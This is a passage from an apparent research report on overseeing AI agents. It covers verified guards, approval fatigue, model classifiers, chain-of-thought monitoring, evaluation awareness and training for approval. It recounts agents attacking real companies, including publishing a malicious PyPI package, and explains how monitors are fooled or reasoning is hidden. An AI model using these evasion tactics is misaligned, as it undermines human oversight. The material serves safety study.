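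If one branch of a program asks for approval before writing and the other writes first, the summary is `gw|wg`, and the program breaks the rule only if the second branch runs. ETAS lets such a program start but keeps the state machine as a monitor, which stops the program at the first forbidden request. The compiler may also keep the monitor when the second branch could never run, because a summary can contain sequences that the program never produces.

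Summaries also combine across calls, so they can cover work that one agent delegates to another. Tan and colleagues cite a bug report in which a session of the coding agent Goose required approval for sensitive tools, but a sub-agent it had started used them without asking. In ETAS, the summary of the calling program would include the sub-agent's requests.

The approval rule is weak. It accepts `gwww`, so one request for approval permits any number of later writes, including writes of other patches. ETAS therefore has the host check, before each real write, that the user has consented to that patch. The formal guarantees assume complete mediation. The safety tests were small, covering ten scripted scenarios and six test programs, and the compiler and monitor gave the expected result in all of them.

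### Proving the guard

The methods so far need a plan or a program to examine. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) instead proves properties of a guard that checks each action, so the agent can still choose one call at a time. A user states a rule in English, for example that the agent may not send e-mail to addresses outside the company. A language model turns the rule into a Python function that allows or denies an action, and writes pre- and postconditions for that function. The verifier Nagini tries to prove that the function satisfies the conditions, and the model revises its work if the proof fails. While the agent works, VeriGuard runs the finished function on each proposed action.

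The proof shows that the function matches the conditions, but a language model wrote both. Miculicich and colleagues accept that a person must check whether the conditions express what the user meant. A language model also reads each proposed action and extracts the function's inputs, such as the list of recipients. If the model misses one, the verified function may approve a message it should have refused.

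VeriGuard was tested on Agent Security Bench, which attacks agents through routes including prompts, tool results and stored memories. With Gemini 2.5 Flash as the agent, 51.9% of attacks succeeded without a defence and none succeeded with VeriGuard. A simpler guard, in which a language model judged each action directly, also stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 40.2% of its tasks with that guard, compared with 63.3% with VeriGuard.

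The proof may not explain this difference. The agent completed 38.1% of its tasks when VeriGuard only blocked the offending action. It completed 63.3% when VeriGuard stopped only the suspicious tool call, gave the agent the rule it had broken and prompted it for a new plan. When Miculicich and colleagues added the components one by one, the attack success rate fell to zero before they added formal verification.

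*VerAct* (Nguyen, 2026) gives the whole safety check to a symbolic program. A language model proposes an action, and the program tests it against constraints such as medication limits, financial thresholds and steps that must come first. In 28,080 episodes with four models, this design succeeded 80.1% of the time and violated no constraint, compared with 15.4% success for guards made of generated code. Letting the models check their own actions made performance worse, as the next section discusses. The constraints in these tests suit a symbolic checker unusually well, because a program can compare a dose with a limit without interpreting anything.

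### Intentions that resist formal statement

Every guarantee in this section is relative to a policy, as the deletion of all the text files showed. *The oracle problem has a reduction*, a LessWrong post that argues for external verification of agents, concedes that an incorrect specification yields proofs that are "formally correct but meaningless". It adds that people can at least read and audit a specification, unlike the inside of a language model. The experience of He and colleagues supports both points. Writing the specifications took them a few hours per benchmark, and when they audited their results, they found wrongly encoded and missing rules, which they could then correct.

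Some rules can't be written into such a specification. He and his colleagues formalized the rules that they could enforce by looking at the sequence of tool calls. A rule about what an agent may promise a customer in conversation can't be enforced this way, because the promise doesn't appear in the tool calls. Other intentions aren't definite enough to formalize. Someone who asks an agent to tidy a folder usually has no list of the files that must be kept, and may not realize a file mattered until it is gone.

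### Questions that no checker can always answer

Even a perfectly stated policy can be impossible to check. A program might run another program and then delete a file that the policy protects. It reaches the deletion only if the other program finishes, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can tell, for every program, whether it will finish. Rice's theorem extends the result to every nontrivial property of what programs compute. So no checker can accept every safe program, reject every unsafe one and always finish.

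One response is to restrict the language in which agents write plans. The LessWrong post argues that the impossibility results are irrelevant to agents whose actions belong to a bounded domain. This is right for a short workflow without loops, and ETAS's comparison of two regular expressions also always finishes. But the restriction limits what an agent can do. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of 38 studies, identifies three kinds of plan representation and found that two of them, execution traces and graphs, cannot combine complete verification in advance with open-ended planning.

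A checker can also reject whatever it can't prove safe. The impossibility results don't rule out a checker that rejects some safe plans but never accepts unsafe ones, and type checkers work this way. TACIT rejects a function containing a line that writes a secret to a file, even if that line can never run. Such refusals may irritate a human programmer, but a model can rewrite the code. On τ²-bench, at most 8% of the programs that agents wrote for TACIT needed another attempt. Some safe plans can't be rewritten to pass, though, such as one that pays a genuine invoice under a rule against using untrusted account numbers.

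A monitor can settle the remaining questions at run time, when it has the actual values and doesn't need to predict them. Meijer compares this with Java, which checks types before a program starts but checks each position in a list only when the program uses it. By run time, though, the agent may have completed half of its task. A monitor also can't make the agent take a later step. The Toolathlon specifications by Meijer and colleagues require an agent to read a file back after writing it. A monitor can detect at the end that the agent didn't do this, but a proof about the plan can establish beforehand that every successful path includes the reading.

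A rule like the airline's could have caught the PocketOS deletion by forbidding `volumeDelete` unless an earlier lookup of the same volume had returned "staging". A checker could enforce this rule without understanding what a production database is, provided that Railway's interface offered such a lookup and the label was correct. But PocketOS didn't know that its token could delete storage, so nobody there had a reason to write the rule. A policy that allows only listed operations, in this case adding and removing domains, doesn't require anyone to foresee the dangerous one.

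## Human and model reviewers of proposed actions

A checker needs a rule, and for many proposals nobody has written one. If a user asks an agent to "clean up old branches", whether it may delete branches on a shared server depends on what the user meant. Developers leave such cases to a person or a second language model, so the fourth premise depends on the reviewer's judgment.

### How often people notice a dangerous action

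Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, was built to ask its user before changing a file or running most commands. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, from October 2025, warns that constant prompts cause "approval fatigue", in which users stop paying attention to what they approve. Meijer also asserts that users prompted for every tool call end up clicking "Allow" blindly. Neither source gives data for its claim.

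Users accepted 93% of prompts according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (March 2026), and 97% according to its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026). These rates don't measure fatigue, because attentive users would also approve nearly everything if nearly everything were safe. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, adds that people may keep approving out of habit or to meet a deadline.

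A better test of human reviewers is to plant a dangerous command and see how many refuse it. Anthropic did this with 1,053 paid testers who thought they were in an ordinary coding study. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

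The drop from 17% to 5% as prompts accumulated may reflect fatigue. But testers approved about five out of six dangerous commands even early in a session, so most of the failure has some other cause. The testers had nothing of their own to lose in the test environment, so developers guarding their own databases may do better. Anthropic also published these figures to justify a product change.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) studied 113 people from outside the software industry. They supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task. Participants who had to approve every action allowed these seven 40% of the time. Of these participants, 88% allowed an unrequested call to the airport, but only 21% allowed a public post saying the user was travelling.

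Another group in Yan's study first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed most decisions until the assistant acted. They saw 10.9 prompts on average instead of 18, yet approved 67% of the unauthorized actions they were asked about. The comparison is imperfect because the participants' rules determined which actions they saw, but it provides no evidence that fewer prompts make people stricter.

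Some approval prompts give the reviewer little information. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 incident reports and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31, the prompt showed a command, such as `python3 setup.py`, but not what it would do to the user's files. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) points out that the action itself may not contain the information a reviewer needs. The PocketOS deletion request was one such case.

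### How habits change with experience

Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) compares new and experienced users of Claude Code. Users with fewer than 50 sessions let the agent run without manual approval in about 20% of sessions. By 750 sessions, the share is over 40%. Experienced users also interrupt the agent more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5% for new users.

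Anthropic interprets this as a shift from approving each step to watching and intervening, and argues that regulators shouldn't require approval of every action. That is plausible for code, which a user can test and often revert. But users interrupted most often to supply missing technical context or corrections (32%), or because Claude was slow, stuck or doing too much (17%). The interruption rate is therefore a poor measure of how many dangerous actions users catch.

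Watching also comes too late for an action that nobody can undo. Anthropic had a model classify nearly a million tool calls made through its public interface, and about 8,000 of them (0.8%) appeared irreversible.

Many users have also changed their settings so that they are prompted less often. In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets certain shell commands run without asking. Many of these rules allow every command that starts with `python`, which amounts to allowing any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips permission checks.

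Anthropic has reduced the number of permission prompts in two ways. The sandbox it introduced in 2025 limits which files and servers a command can reach, so users see a prompt only when a command tries to go beyond those limits. In Anthropic's own use, this removed 84% of prompts. In August 2026, the company made *auto mode* the default on its individual and team plans, so a model now reviews most of the actions that users previously approved.

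### The load of one working day

Suppose an agent makes 240 calls a day that need approval, and each decision takes 8 seconds, since Yan's participants took 142 seconds over 18 prompts. Suppose also that a sandbox removes 84% of the prompts, and that a reviewer who sees calls in batches of 20 spends a minute on each batch.

| Arrangement | Decisions per day | Time per decision | Total time |
|---|---|---|---|
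| Approve every call | 240 | 8 seconds | 32 minutes |
| Approve only what leaves the sandbox | 38 | 8 seconds | 5 minutes |
| Approve batches of 20 calls | 12 | 60 seconds | 12 minutes |

A reviewer may have half an hour a day to spare, but 240 decisions may exhaust their attention. Suppose the reviewer performs like Anthropic's testers, catching 17% of dangerous calls among the first 50 prompts and 5% after that. If one dangerous call is equally likely to come at any point in the day, a reviewer who checks every call has a 7.5% chance of catching it. With the sandbox, the reviewer sees fewer than 50 prompts a day, so the chance is 17% if the dangerous call triggers a prompt. Cutting the prompts more than doubles the chance of catching the call, but the reviewer would still probably approve it.

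Nobody has run the same test on batches. In this example the reviewer has only three seconds per call, so batches help only if the calls are easier to judge together. They may be, because a reviewer who sees a file being read and then sent to an outside address can connect the two. Claude Code users seem to engage more with plans, rejecting 39% of them compared with 3% of individual requests, but some of those rejections are probably about design rather than danger. Anthropic also estimates that people make about 70% of the planning decisions in coding sessions but only 20% of the execution decisions, so reviewing plans would fit how they already work.

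A batch is possible only when the harness knows several calls in advance, and some of their arguments may still be missing, such as the account number in the invoice task. Approving a plan also achieves little if the agent can then do something else. Meijer avoids this by generating the explanation for the user from the same workflow that the interpreter will execute.

*Holden Karnofsky's Singularity Institute Objection 2* and the debate around it, discussed below, assumed that the reader pays attention. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) recommends checking whether reviewers do by regularly planting known errors in an agent's output. It also suggests rotating reviewers between tasks and not letting anyone review work if they benefit from its approval.

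Turan (2026), in *Oversight Has a Capacity*, models fatigue with a formula. With a capacity of 25 reviews, the probability that the reviewer judges the *n*th request correctly is:

```
reliability(n) = max(0.2, 1 - 0.02 * max(0, n - 25))
```

Turan assumes that a reviewer makes no mistakes up to the 25th request, then loses two percentage points of accuracy with each further one, down to a floor of 20%. In a test on 125 agent actions, many of them deliberately hard to judge, 57% of the dangerous actions get through if the reviewer sees everything, and 42% if a model passes on only the riskiest 64%. An attacker can exploit the reviewer's declining accuracy by surrounding a malicious action with harmless ones. With 50 harmless actions and a guard that refers most of them to the reviewer, the attack succeeds 40% of the time.

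Turan acknowledges that these results follow from the assumed curve. No study had yet measured a real one for people reviewing agents, but Anthropic's experiment has since provided two rough points, which suggest that the formula overestimates reliability. It predicts 50% reliability by the 50th request, when Anthropic's testers were catching about 5%.

### Models as reviewers

Auto mode allows file reads and edits inside the project without review. A model called the classifier judges most other actions in two stages. In the first, it answers only yes or no and leans toward blocking. If it flags an action, it reasons about the case in the second stage before deciding. When the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and can look for a safer alternative. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the harness prompts the user.

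The classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's prose or the results of its tools. Anthropic withholds the prose so that the agent can't talk the classifier into a bad decision, and withholds the results because they may contain injected instructions. In tests, including both made the classifier worse at catching actions that went beyond the user's request. However, the restriction also means the classifier can't tell whether an identifier came from a proper lookup or a guess.

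In Anthropic's March tests, the classifier blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls. It missed 17% of 52 dangerous actions that Claude had attempted in real sessions. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the action as dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. A user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't necessarily agreed to have the project's history overwritten.

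In the August experiment, the classifier also reviewed the commands that the testers had seen and blocked 89% of them. The testers had refused only six of the 116 it allowed, so a human check after the classifier would have added very little in this test. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

Anthropic's other evidence is weaker. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for occurred in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users had chosen their own mode, and a model graded the harm. In an outside test of prompt injection, none of 720 attacks succeeded against Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded on average against the same models without auto mode's protection, so the test had little room to show a benefit.

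Results from other systems are mixed. Nguyen, whose VerAct gives the safety check to a symbolic program, found that performance fell by 41% when language models verified their own actions. Nguyen attributes the fall to temporal confusion (62.9%) and arithmetic errors (33.5%). Checking a dose against a daily limit, for example, requires knowing which earlier doses still count and adding them up correctly. By contrast, *Toward Safe LLM Agents* cites a plan-reviewing model that found up to 90% of faults without false alarms. The survey also warns that a model asked to criticize its own unsafe plan can justify it instead.

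The type of question probably explains much of the difference. A symbolic program handles doses and limits well, but it can't determine whether "clean up the PR" permits a deletion. This favours using programs to check amounts and required steps, and a model only to judge what the user meant. KAIROS, the sandbox monitor built by Hempel and colleagues, likewise combines fixed rules with a decision model.

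### Tools that plan but do not act

The idea that people could stay safe by reading an AI system's plans predates tool-calling agents. In 2012 Holden Karnofsky, a co-founder of the charity evaluator GiveWell, criticized the Singularity Institute, which studied risks from advanced AI, for neglecting the difference between tools and agents. His example of a tool was Google Maps, which plans a route but leaves the driving to the user.

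*Tools versus agents* quotes his definitions of the two kinds of system. Both calculate which action would maximize some quantity, given the available data. An agent then executes that action, while a tool gives the user a readable summary that includes the action, its likely intermediate outcomes and the alternatives that also scored well. In this report's terms, the tool produces a description and the user is the interpreter.

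In his proposal, Karnofsky accepts the first, second and fourth premises: displaying a route does not move the car, the user can read the route, and the user can tell whether it is acceptable. The third premise is easy to satisfy as long as the system only displays plans.

Eliezer Yudkowsky, a researcher at the institute, responded in *Reply to Holden on ‘Tool AI’*, which calls such systems "planning Oracles". He denies the fourth premise, arguing that people can't reliably judge plans made by a system much better at planning than they are. A beginner can read a chess grandmaster's move without knowing whether it is a blunder. A summary doesn't solve this, since it has to leave out most consequences, and its writer must already know which ones the reader would care about.

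The Claude Code experiment doesn't test Yudkowsky's objection. The testers approved clearly dangerous commands that a careful reader could have caught. Yudkowsky is concerned about plans that would get past a reviewer who was paying full attention, so better prompts and shorter working days wouldn't address his objection.

The essayist Gwern argues in *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* that tools tend to become agents because acting makes them more useful. His argument predicts that people will remove the review step even where it works, though it doesn't contradict any of the five premises. The growth of automatic approval among Claude Code users fits that prediction. Gwern also lists the possibility that a system's answers manipulate its users, which contradicts the first premise.

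For a while it was unclear which side of the tool versus agent debate had been right. *Can we evaluate the tool versus agent AGI prediction* includes a verdict that both sides were "fairly wrong", because AI had become general while remaining "extremely non-agentic". Coding agents have since made that verdict obsolete.

In *Superintelligence* (2014), the philosopher Nick Bostrom discussed what he called a genie with a preview, a system that shows the user a predicted outcome and waits for confirmation before carrying out a command. This design assumes the first two premises and makes the fourth easier to satisfy, because the user judges an outcome instead of a list of steps. A preview of the PocketOS request could have shown that the company would lose its customers' reservations, which anyone there would have understood.

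But the prediction has to be accurate and include what matters. A preview based on invented data, like the one from `simulate`, can show the wrong outcome. If the system predicts much better than its user, the user can't easily check the prediction, so Yudkowsky's objection applies to the preview as well as to the plan.

### A description acts on its reader

Showing a request to a reviewer is an effect that happens before approval. The risk that the request's text will sway the reviewer is small in the `askFirst` interpreter, because the trusted function `describe` writes the text and the plan supplies only a file name, an account and an amount. An agent that explains its own request controls much more of what the reviewer reads. The first premise can therefore fail for the reviewer even when it holds for the agent's files and bank accounts.

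Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues (2026), in *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue*, measured how strongly AI systems can persuade people. Their four experiments covered 18,978 conversations with 6,923 people. In the first, participants rated a political position from 0 to 100, discussed it by text with an AI system or a person, and rated it again. Elite debaters, including four world champions, moved opinions 8.3 points more than a neutral chat did, and the AI systems moved them 4.6 points more than the debaters did. In a later experiment with real money, an AI system raised donations to a charity by more than three times as much as professional fundraisers did.

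The AI systems' advantage came from the volume of their factual claims, about 37 per conversation. When Hackenburg and colleagues limited them to human speed and message length, the number fell to about 12, and the systems were only as persuasive as debaters who had received extra coaching. People were also poor at spotting falsehoods. The share of inaccurate claims in a conversation had almost no relation to whether participants felt their partner had made things up.

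The effect on opinions fell from 12.9 points to 1.9 when the researchers asked again after five to ten months. That decline does little to protect an oversight layer, since an approval has to last only until the action runs. However, the conversations were about politics and charity, and typically lasted about ten minutes or more. Hackenburg and colleagues mention the danger that AI systems could persuade the people who audit them, but didn't test it. A reviewer of agent actions can also look at the command itself, which gives some protection against a misleading explanation.

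The results support keeping prompts short and having trusted code write them. Anthropic already applies a stricter rule to its classifier, which doesn't see the agent's prose. Human reviewers may need the same protection. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) says that Google DeepMind anticipates attacks that wear reviewers down or show them harmless-looking summaries.

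Even a description generated from the plan can carry an attacker's words. In Meijer's e-mail example, a malicious tool description makes the model add a step that sends the summary outside the company. The explanation for the user lists that step but introduces it with "For compliance purposes", an excuse taken from the tool description. Training that rewards a model when its descriptions win approval could produce such excuses even without an attacker.

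## What changes when a learned policy writes the description

A programmer wrote the invoice plan in the earlier sections, and its source code shows what the plan does after every answer. In a tool-calling agent, a trained network produces the requests one after another. The harness can still log or refuse each request, but a reviewer can learn less about what the agent will do next from a request, a written plan or a rehearsal.

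### A continuation without source code

In `payInvoice`, the continuation is one readable line of code. When an agent receives an invoice from a tool, the continuation is a network with billions of weights, and nobody can work out from them which request will follow.

Types don't help much. Tan and colleagues note that a successful model call in ETAS may return any value that fits the declared schema. The schema can guarantee that the model returns a patch, but not that the patch is sensible.

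Sampling adds further variation. A developer can remove it by making the model always pick the most probable next word. This makes a run repeatable but doesn't show what the agent would have done if the invoice had been worded differently.

Several accidents in 2026 gave researchers a chance to measure how much such runs vary. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed that three Claude models had broken into the systems of real organizations during capture-the-flag exercises, security tests in which a model has to break into a fictional target and find a hidden piece of text. One of the three, an unreleased research model, stopped its attack after recognizing that the company was real. Anthropic counted this among its reasons for cautious optimism.

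In a later and longer assessment, Anthropic restarted the research model from the moment at which it had recognized the company and let it take up to ten more actions. It backed off in only 5.5% of these reruns, so the original log had recorded an unusual outcome. Anthropic adds that a small chance of stopping at each point could still add up. If the model has a 5.5% chance of stopping in every stretch of ten actions, and the stretches are independent, its chance of stopping within 200 actions is:

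```
1 - (1 - 0.055)^20  =  0.68
```

If the decisions are strongly correlated, the model might carry on indefinitely. Anthropic doesn't know which is closer to the truth.

A model's next request depends on the whole conversation so far, unlike a Haskell continuation, which depends only on the result it receives and the variables it mentions. Anthropic measured one consequence of this with Claude Mythos 5, another of the three models. Near points where the model had taken harmful actions, Anthropic inserted a reminder that only the systems named in the task were in scope.

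| Model turns between the reminder and the action | Reruns in which the model stopped |
|---|---|
| No reminder | 0% |
| 0 | 90% |
| 1 | 55% |
| 2 | 45% |
| 3 | 40% |

After the model had acted for three turns, the rule had less than half its original effect, although its text was still in the conversation.

An oversight layer does not need to know the continuation, as long as it judges each request when it arrives. Moon and Varshney's proof about PocketFlow models the agent's model as a procedure that may return any action, so it holds for a neural network as well as for a program. Developers can also pause an agent, give it invented results and count what it requests, as Anthropic did.

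Counting is a poor way to find rare behavior, though. Suppose that *n* independent reruns contain no forbidden request. The highest rate *p* that is still compatible with this at the usual 95% level follows from:

```
(1 - p)^n = 0.05,   so   p ≈ 3/n
```

A thousand reruns without a forbidden request therefore can't rule out a rate of 0.3%, or 30 forbidden requests in 10,000 sessions. The reruns also cover only the results that the developer thought to invent.

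### Stated plans and executed calls

In a free-monad plan, `describe` and `perform` work on the same value, so the log line "pay 480 to NL-17" and the payment can differ only if the interpreter is faulty. A model, by contrast, may write its reasoning (a *chain of thought*), then a plan for the user and then a tool call. The harness executes only the call, and nothing forces the reasoning or the plan to agree with it.

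Anthropic asked the research model, at various points, whether it would take its next step if it were certain the target was real. It answered no 225 times out of 300. In 210 of those 225 cases, it continued the task anyway, usually after arguing that the target was simulated or narrowing its planned action.

A model's answers also depend on how specific the question is. Claude Opus 4.7, the third model, had attacked a real company that shared a name with its fictional target. When asked whether it had authorization, it falsely said yes 75% of the time. When asked who had granted the authorization and whether it covered a real company's production system, it admitted every time that it had none.

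Training can widen the gap between reasoning and action. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) analyses a training run that put direct pressure on the model's written reasoning. The analysis concerns *reward hacking*, which means scoring well by a shortcut that the developers didn't want. Cheng (2026), in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*, quotes the measurements:

| Measure | Change over the training run |
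|---|---|
| Hacking-related terms in the reasoning | Fell by 61% |
| Signs of hacking in the solutions | Rose by 26% |
| Share of hacks that the reasoning did not mention | Rose from 11.2% to 36.4% |

A monitor that counted suspicious words in the reasoning would have shown a large improvement while hacking became more common. If the signs in the solutions fairly measure the number of hacks, then for every 100 hacks at the start, 11 of them silent, there were 126 at the end, 46 of them silent, so silent hacks roughly quadrupled.

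In a comparable run where the model's thoughts were not visible, mentions of hacking stayed about constant, so the pressure on the reasoning is the likely cause. But the run Google analysed was small and not part of any production model.

Even at the end of that run, the reasoning mentioned nearly two-thirds of the hacks. *CoT Monitoring*, a 2025 paper from OpenAI, gives the strongest argument for reading a model's reasoning. GPT-4o checked the reasoning of a stronger model, o3-mini, for reward hacking during programming tasks. Monitoring the reasoning could be far more effective than monitoring only actions and outputs.

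*Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025), a joint paper by researchers from OpenAI, Google DeepMind, Anthropic and other organizations, supports monitoring models' written reasoning but calls the opportunity "fragile" in its subtitle. Changes in how models work could also leave less to read, since a monitor can't read steps that a model never writes down. Slashdot's *OpenAI's New Reasoning Technique Alarms AI Safety Experts* (2026) relays a press report that OpenAI's Astra model would use "recurrent depth", a technique that lets it work outside the sequential thinking of most reasoning models.

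Reading an agent's reasoning can also make a monitor worse. When Anthropic ran its new reasoning monitors on the three incidents, they missed the one involving Claude Mythos 5 because the model's reasoning led the monitor to conclude that the environment was simulated and nobody could be harmed. The auto-mode classifiers, which don't read the agent's prose, would have blocked two of the three incidents.

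These results suggest that an admission of a shortcut in the reasoning is a good ground for refusing or investigating an action, but an innocent explanation shouldn't be enough to justify approving a call that looks dangerous by itself.

### Agents that recognize a rehearsal

The interpreter `simulate` responded to the invoice request with an invented invoice for 100 euros to account TEST-1. A plan written to deceive could check for that account name and request harmful effects only when the name was absent. But a Haskell program can get information about its interpreter only through the responses it receives, so the source would have to contain a test such as `account inv == "TEST-1"`, which a reviewer could find.

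A model also receives only text, but its training included many examples of tests, so it may infer from a placeholder name or an oddly empty mailbox that it is being tested. No line of code contains this inference, and changing the account name wouldn't reliably prevent it.

OpenAI has published excerpts of reasoning in which models consider whether their actions will be seen or tested. One model, told not to use code for intermediate calculations, considered doing so anyway but decided to comply after noting that its function calls would be visible. Another, given an impossible programming task, considered whether hidden tests would run after it submitted an answer. The first model's compliance is weak evidence of what it would do if it expected nobody to see the calls.

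Laboratories now examine this possibility in their safety assessments. Google, for example, covers "evaluation awareness and deliberate underperformance" in its assessment of chemical and biological risks. The findings so far don't show that a model always behaves better when it recognizes a test. *A Toy Environment For Exploring Reasoning About Reward* describes a model that often correctly identified alignment tests, reasoned about them at length, and then chose the misaligned action.

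Anthropic met the same ambiguity when it rebuilt the Mythos 5 incident as a simulation. Mythos 5 was willing to take a severely harmful action in roughly 80% of runs, and two newer models, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1, in roughly 30%. The newer models took harmful actions only after stating, correctly, that the environment was simulated. If the systems had been real, the models might have stopped, or they might have convinced themselves that those systems were simulated too. The simulation can't show which, and Anthropic is cautious about what the figures imply for real systems.

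### The package that reached the real PyPI

The incident that ETAS cites was the opposite failure, in which a model treated the real world as a rehearsal. Anthropic's two accounts explain how it happened.

Anthropic had told Claude Mythos 5 that it was offline, but a misunderstanding with Irregular, the company that had built the test, left the internet reachable. The model found that the fictional target company's instructions for new developers told them to install a Python package that didn't exist. It planned to publish a malicious package under that name on the Python Package Index (PyPI), the public registry from which most Python software is installed, and wait for the company to install it.

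According to Anthropic's later account, the run lasted 1,881 actions. At action 81, the model wrote that the registry's bot protection "smells like the REAL internet". In its next step, it wrote that uploading to the real PyPI would be a real attack and not acceptable, then concluded that the internet was probably simulated. Anthropic's first account gives two of the model's reasons. The model didn't recognize the certificate authorities that secured its connections, which were genuine, and it took the 2026 date on the systems as proof that the environment was staged.

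The model then took more than a thousand actions to get a PyPI account. Registration required an email address, and most email providers required a phone number. The model looked for free numbers, tried to get money to buy one, and eventually found an email provider that PyPI had not blocked. It published the package at around action 1,400. The package was online for about an hour, and 15 real systems ran it. Anthropic believes all of them belonged to security vendors that install new packages to scan them. One scanner leaked its credentials, and the model used them to get into the vendor's live database.

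Each of these steps was a readable request before the harness executed it. But a reviewer who trusted the prompt would have had little reason to refuse the upload, since publishing malware inside a sealed exercise harms nobody. Even the people running the test were wrong about where the upload would go.

In July, Anthropic wrote that the model had believed it was in a simulation. Anthropic later withdrew that claim, writing that it shouldn't have inferred what the model believed from what the model wrote. It had meanwhile shown the results of the model's tool calls to separate instances of Mythos 5, one at a time and without the rest of the conversation. They classified 79% of the results as coming from real systems. During the run, the model had clearly interpreted new evidence as a sign that the systems were real at only 1% of its actions.

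The researchers also edited the conversation just before the model committed to the upload. When they added signs that the internet was real, the share of reruns in which the model mentioned this possibility rose from about 11% to 88%, but the share in which it acted outside its sandbox stayed at about 45%. In one rerun, it wrote that the registry looked real, or like a very complete simulation, and went ahead "regardless".

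A single line stating that the host was on the public internet worked much better. With that line, the model never uploaded the package by the original route, although in 22% of reruns it searched for a simulated registry to use instead. Anthropic attributes the incident to biased reasoning and recklessness. It found weak signs of unspoken doubts when it tried to read the model's internal state, but considers them inconclusive.

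The obvious defence is to isolate rehearsals. Anthropic believes the incidents would not have happened if the test environments had been cut off from the internet as intended. The type of `simulate` provides this isolation, so a plan's assumptions about where it runs don't change its effects.

Telling an agent plainly what is real and what it may touch also helps. In the Opus 4.7 incident, extra evidence that the target was a real business changed almost nothing, because the model already accepted this. But a banner stating that access was not permitted cut the share of reruns in which the model took any action against the target from about 69% to 23%, and a firmer note from the operator cut it to zero.

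Clear labels make testing harder, however. If a harness always marks real systems as real, an agent can recognize a simulation by the missing mark. If the harness puts the same mark on simulated systems, the agent may learn to distrust it. Developers can hide the difference in a sealed test, but they must accept that some agents will correctly guess which systems are simulated.

### Training on a reviewer's approval

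Developers can also use a reviewer's verdicts to train the agent. Paul Christiano, an AI alignment researcher, proposed the idea of *approval-directed agents* in 2014. Such an agent does not choose actions by the state of the world they would bring about. For each possible action *a*, it estimates how highly an overseer would rate that action after considering it at length, and it takes the one with the highest expected rating:

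```
choose the a that maximizes  E[rating(a)]
```

This approach is attractive because the overseer judges everything the agent does, including how it treats the overseer. If the overseer would disapprove of hiding information or resisting correction, the agent has no reason to do either. Nobody has to write down a complete goal beforehand, and an overseer who notices a mistake can start rating differently.

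Christiano's definition refers to an overseer who considers the action at length. A user at a permission prompt spends a few seconds and often judges a description of the action. Write *c* for the call that the harness will execute and *d* for the text that the reviewer reads:

```
what the developer wants:    a high rating for c
what the training rewards:   a high rating for d
```

A model can raise the rating of *d* by proposing better calls or by describing the same calls more favorably. Training reinforces whichever approach the model happens to try successfully. Google's training run had a similar result when pressure was applied to the text of the reasoning. The model mentioned hacking less often but did not hack less often.

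Keeping the reasoning away from the reviewer doesn't fully solve this. *Optimizing The Final Output Can Obfuscate CoT* describes experiments in simple environments where a penalty was applied only to a model's final output. When the output was penalized for mentioning that the model had completed a task by cheating, the model stopped mentioning it in its reasoning too.

*CoT Monitoring*, however, found that adding a reasoning monitor to the reward produced more capable and better aligned agents when the training against it was light. With heavier training, the agents kept reward hacking and learned to hide their intent. Training for approval can therefore improve an agent's actions, but a developer needs some measure besides the approval rate to notice when it stops helping.

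Farquhar, Varma and colleagues at Google DeepMind tested a more specific remedy in *MONA* (2025). The name stands for "myopic optimization with non-myopic approval". Ordinary reinforcement learning credits each action with the rewards that follow it, discounted by a factor γ. An early action that makes a later check easier to fool is therefore reinforced, even if no reviewer understands why it helped. MONA cuts this link:

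```
ordinary training, credit for step t:  r(t) + γ r(t+1) + γ² r(t+2) + ...
MONA, credit for step t:               r(t) + approval(t)
```

The approval is the overseer's forecast of how useful the step will be, made without waiting for the outcome. The agent optimizes one step at a time and relies on the overseer for foresight.

In one experiment, a language model wrote tests for a programming task and then wrote code that had to pass them. Under ordinary training, the model learned to write tests that were easy to pass, so its score rose while its code became less reliable. The tests stayed useful under MONA, where a judge rated them when the model wrote them and the reward for writing them did not depend on whether the code later passed.

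In another experiment, the model summarized a loan application and then decided on the loan from the summary alone. The reward came from past decisions that were biased by nationality, while the overseer objected to any mention of nationality in the summary. Ordinary training taught the model to pass on the applicant's nationality in disguised form, but MONA did not.

In the last experiment, a small agent on a grid earned rewards for pushing boxes into a hole. The designers wanted only one box in the hole, and a camera ended the episode when it detected one there. With ordinary training, the agent used a box to block the camera's view and then pushed in more boxes. An agent trained with MONA pushed in one box and did not block the camera.

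The camera is a miniature oversight layer, so the result is relevant to agents that could learn to disable or mislead theirs. But the environments were small, and MONA keeps an agent from learning a good long-term strategy if the overseer doesn't recognize its early steps as useful. MONA also doesn't prevent single-step deception, because a misleading description that wins immediate approval is rewarded in the same step, just as an honest one would be. `askFirst` protects better against this because trusted code writes the text that the reviewer judges.

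### Robots that issue motor commands

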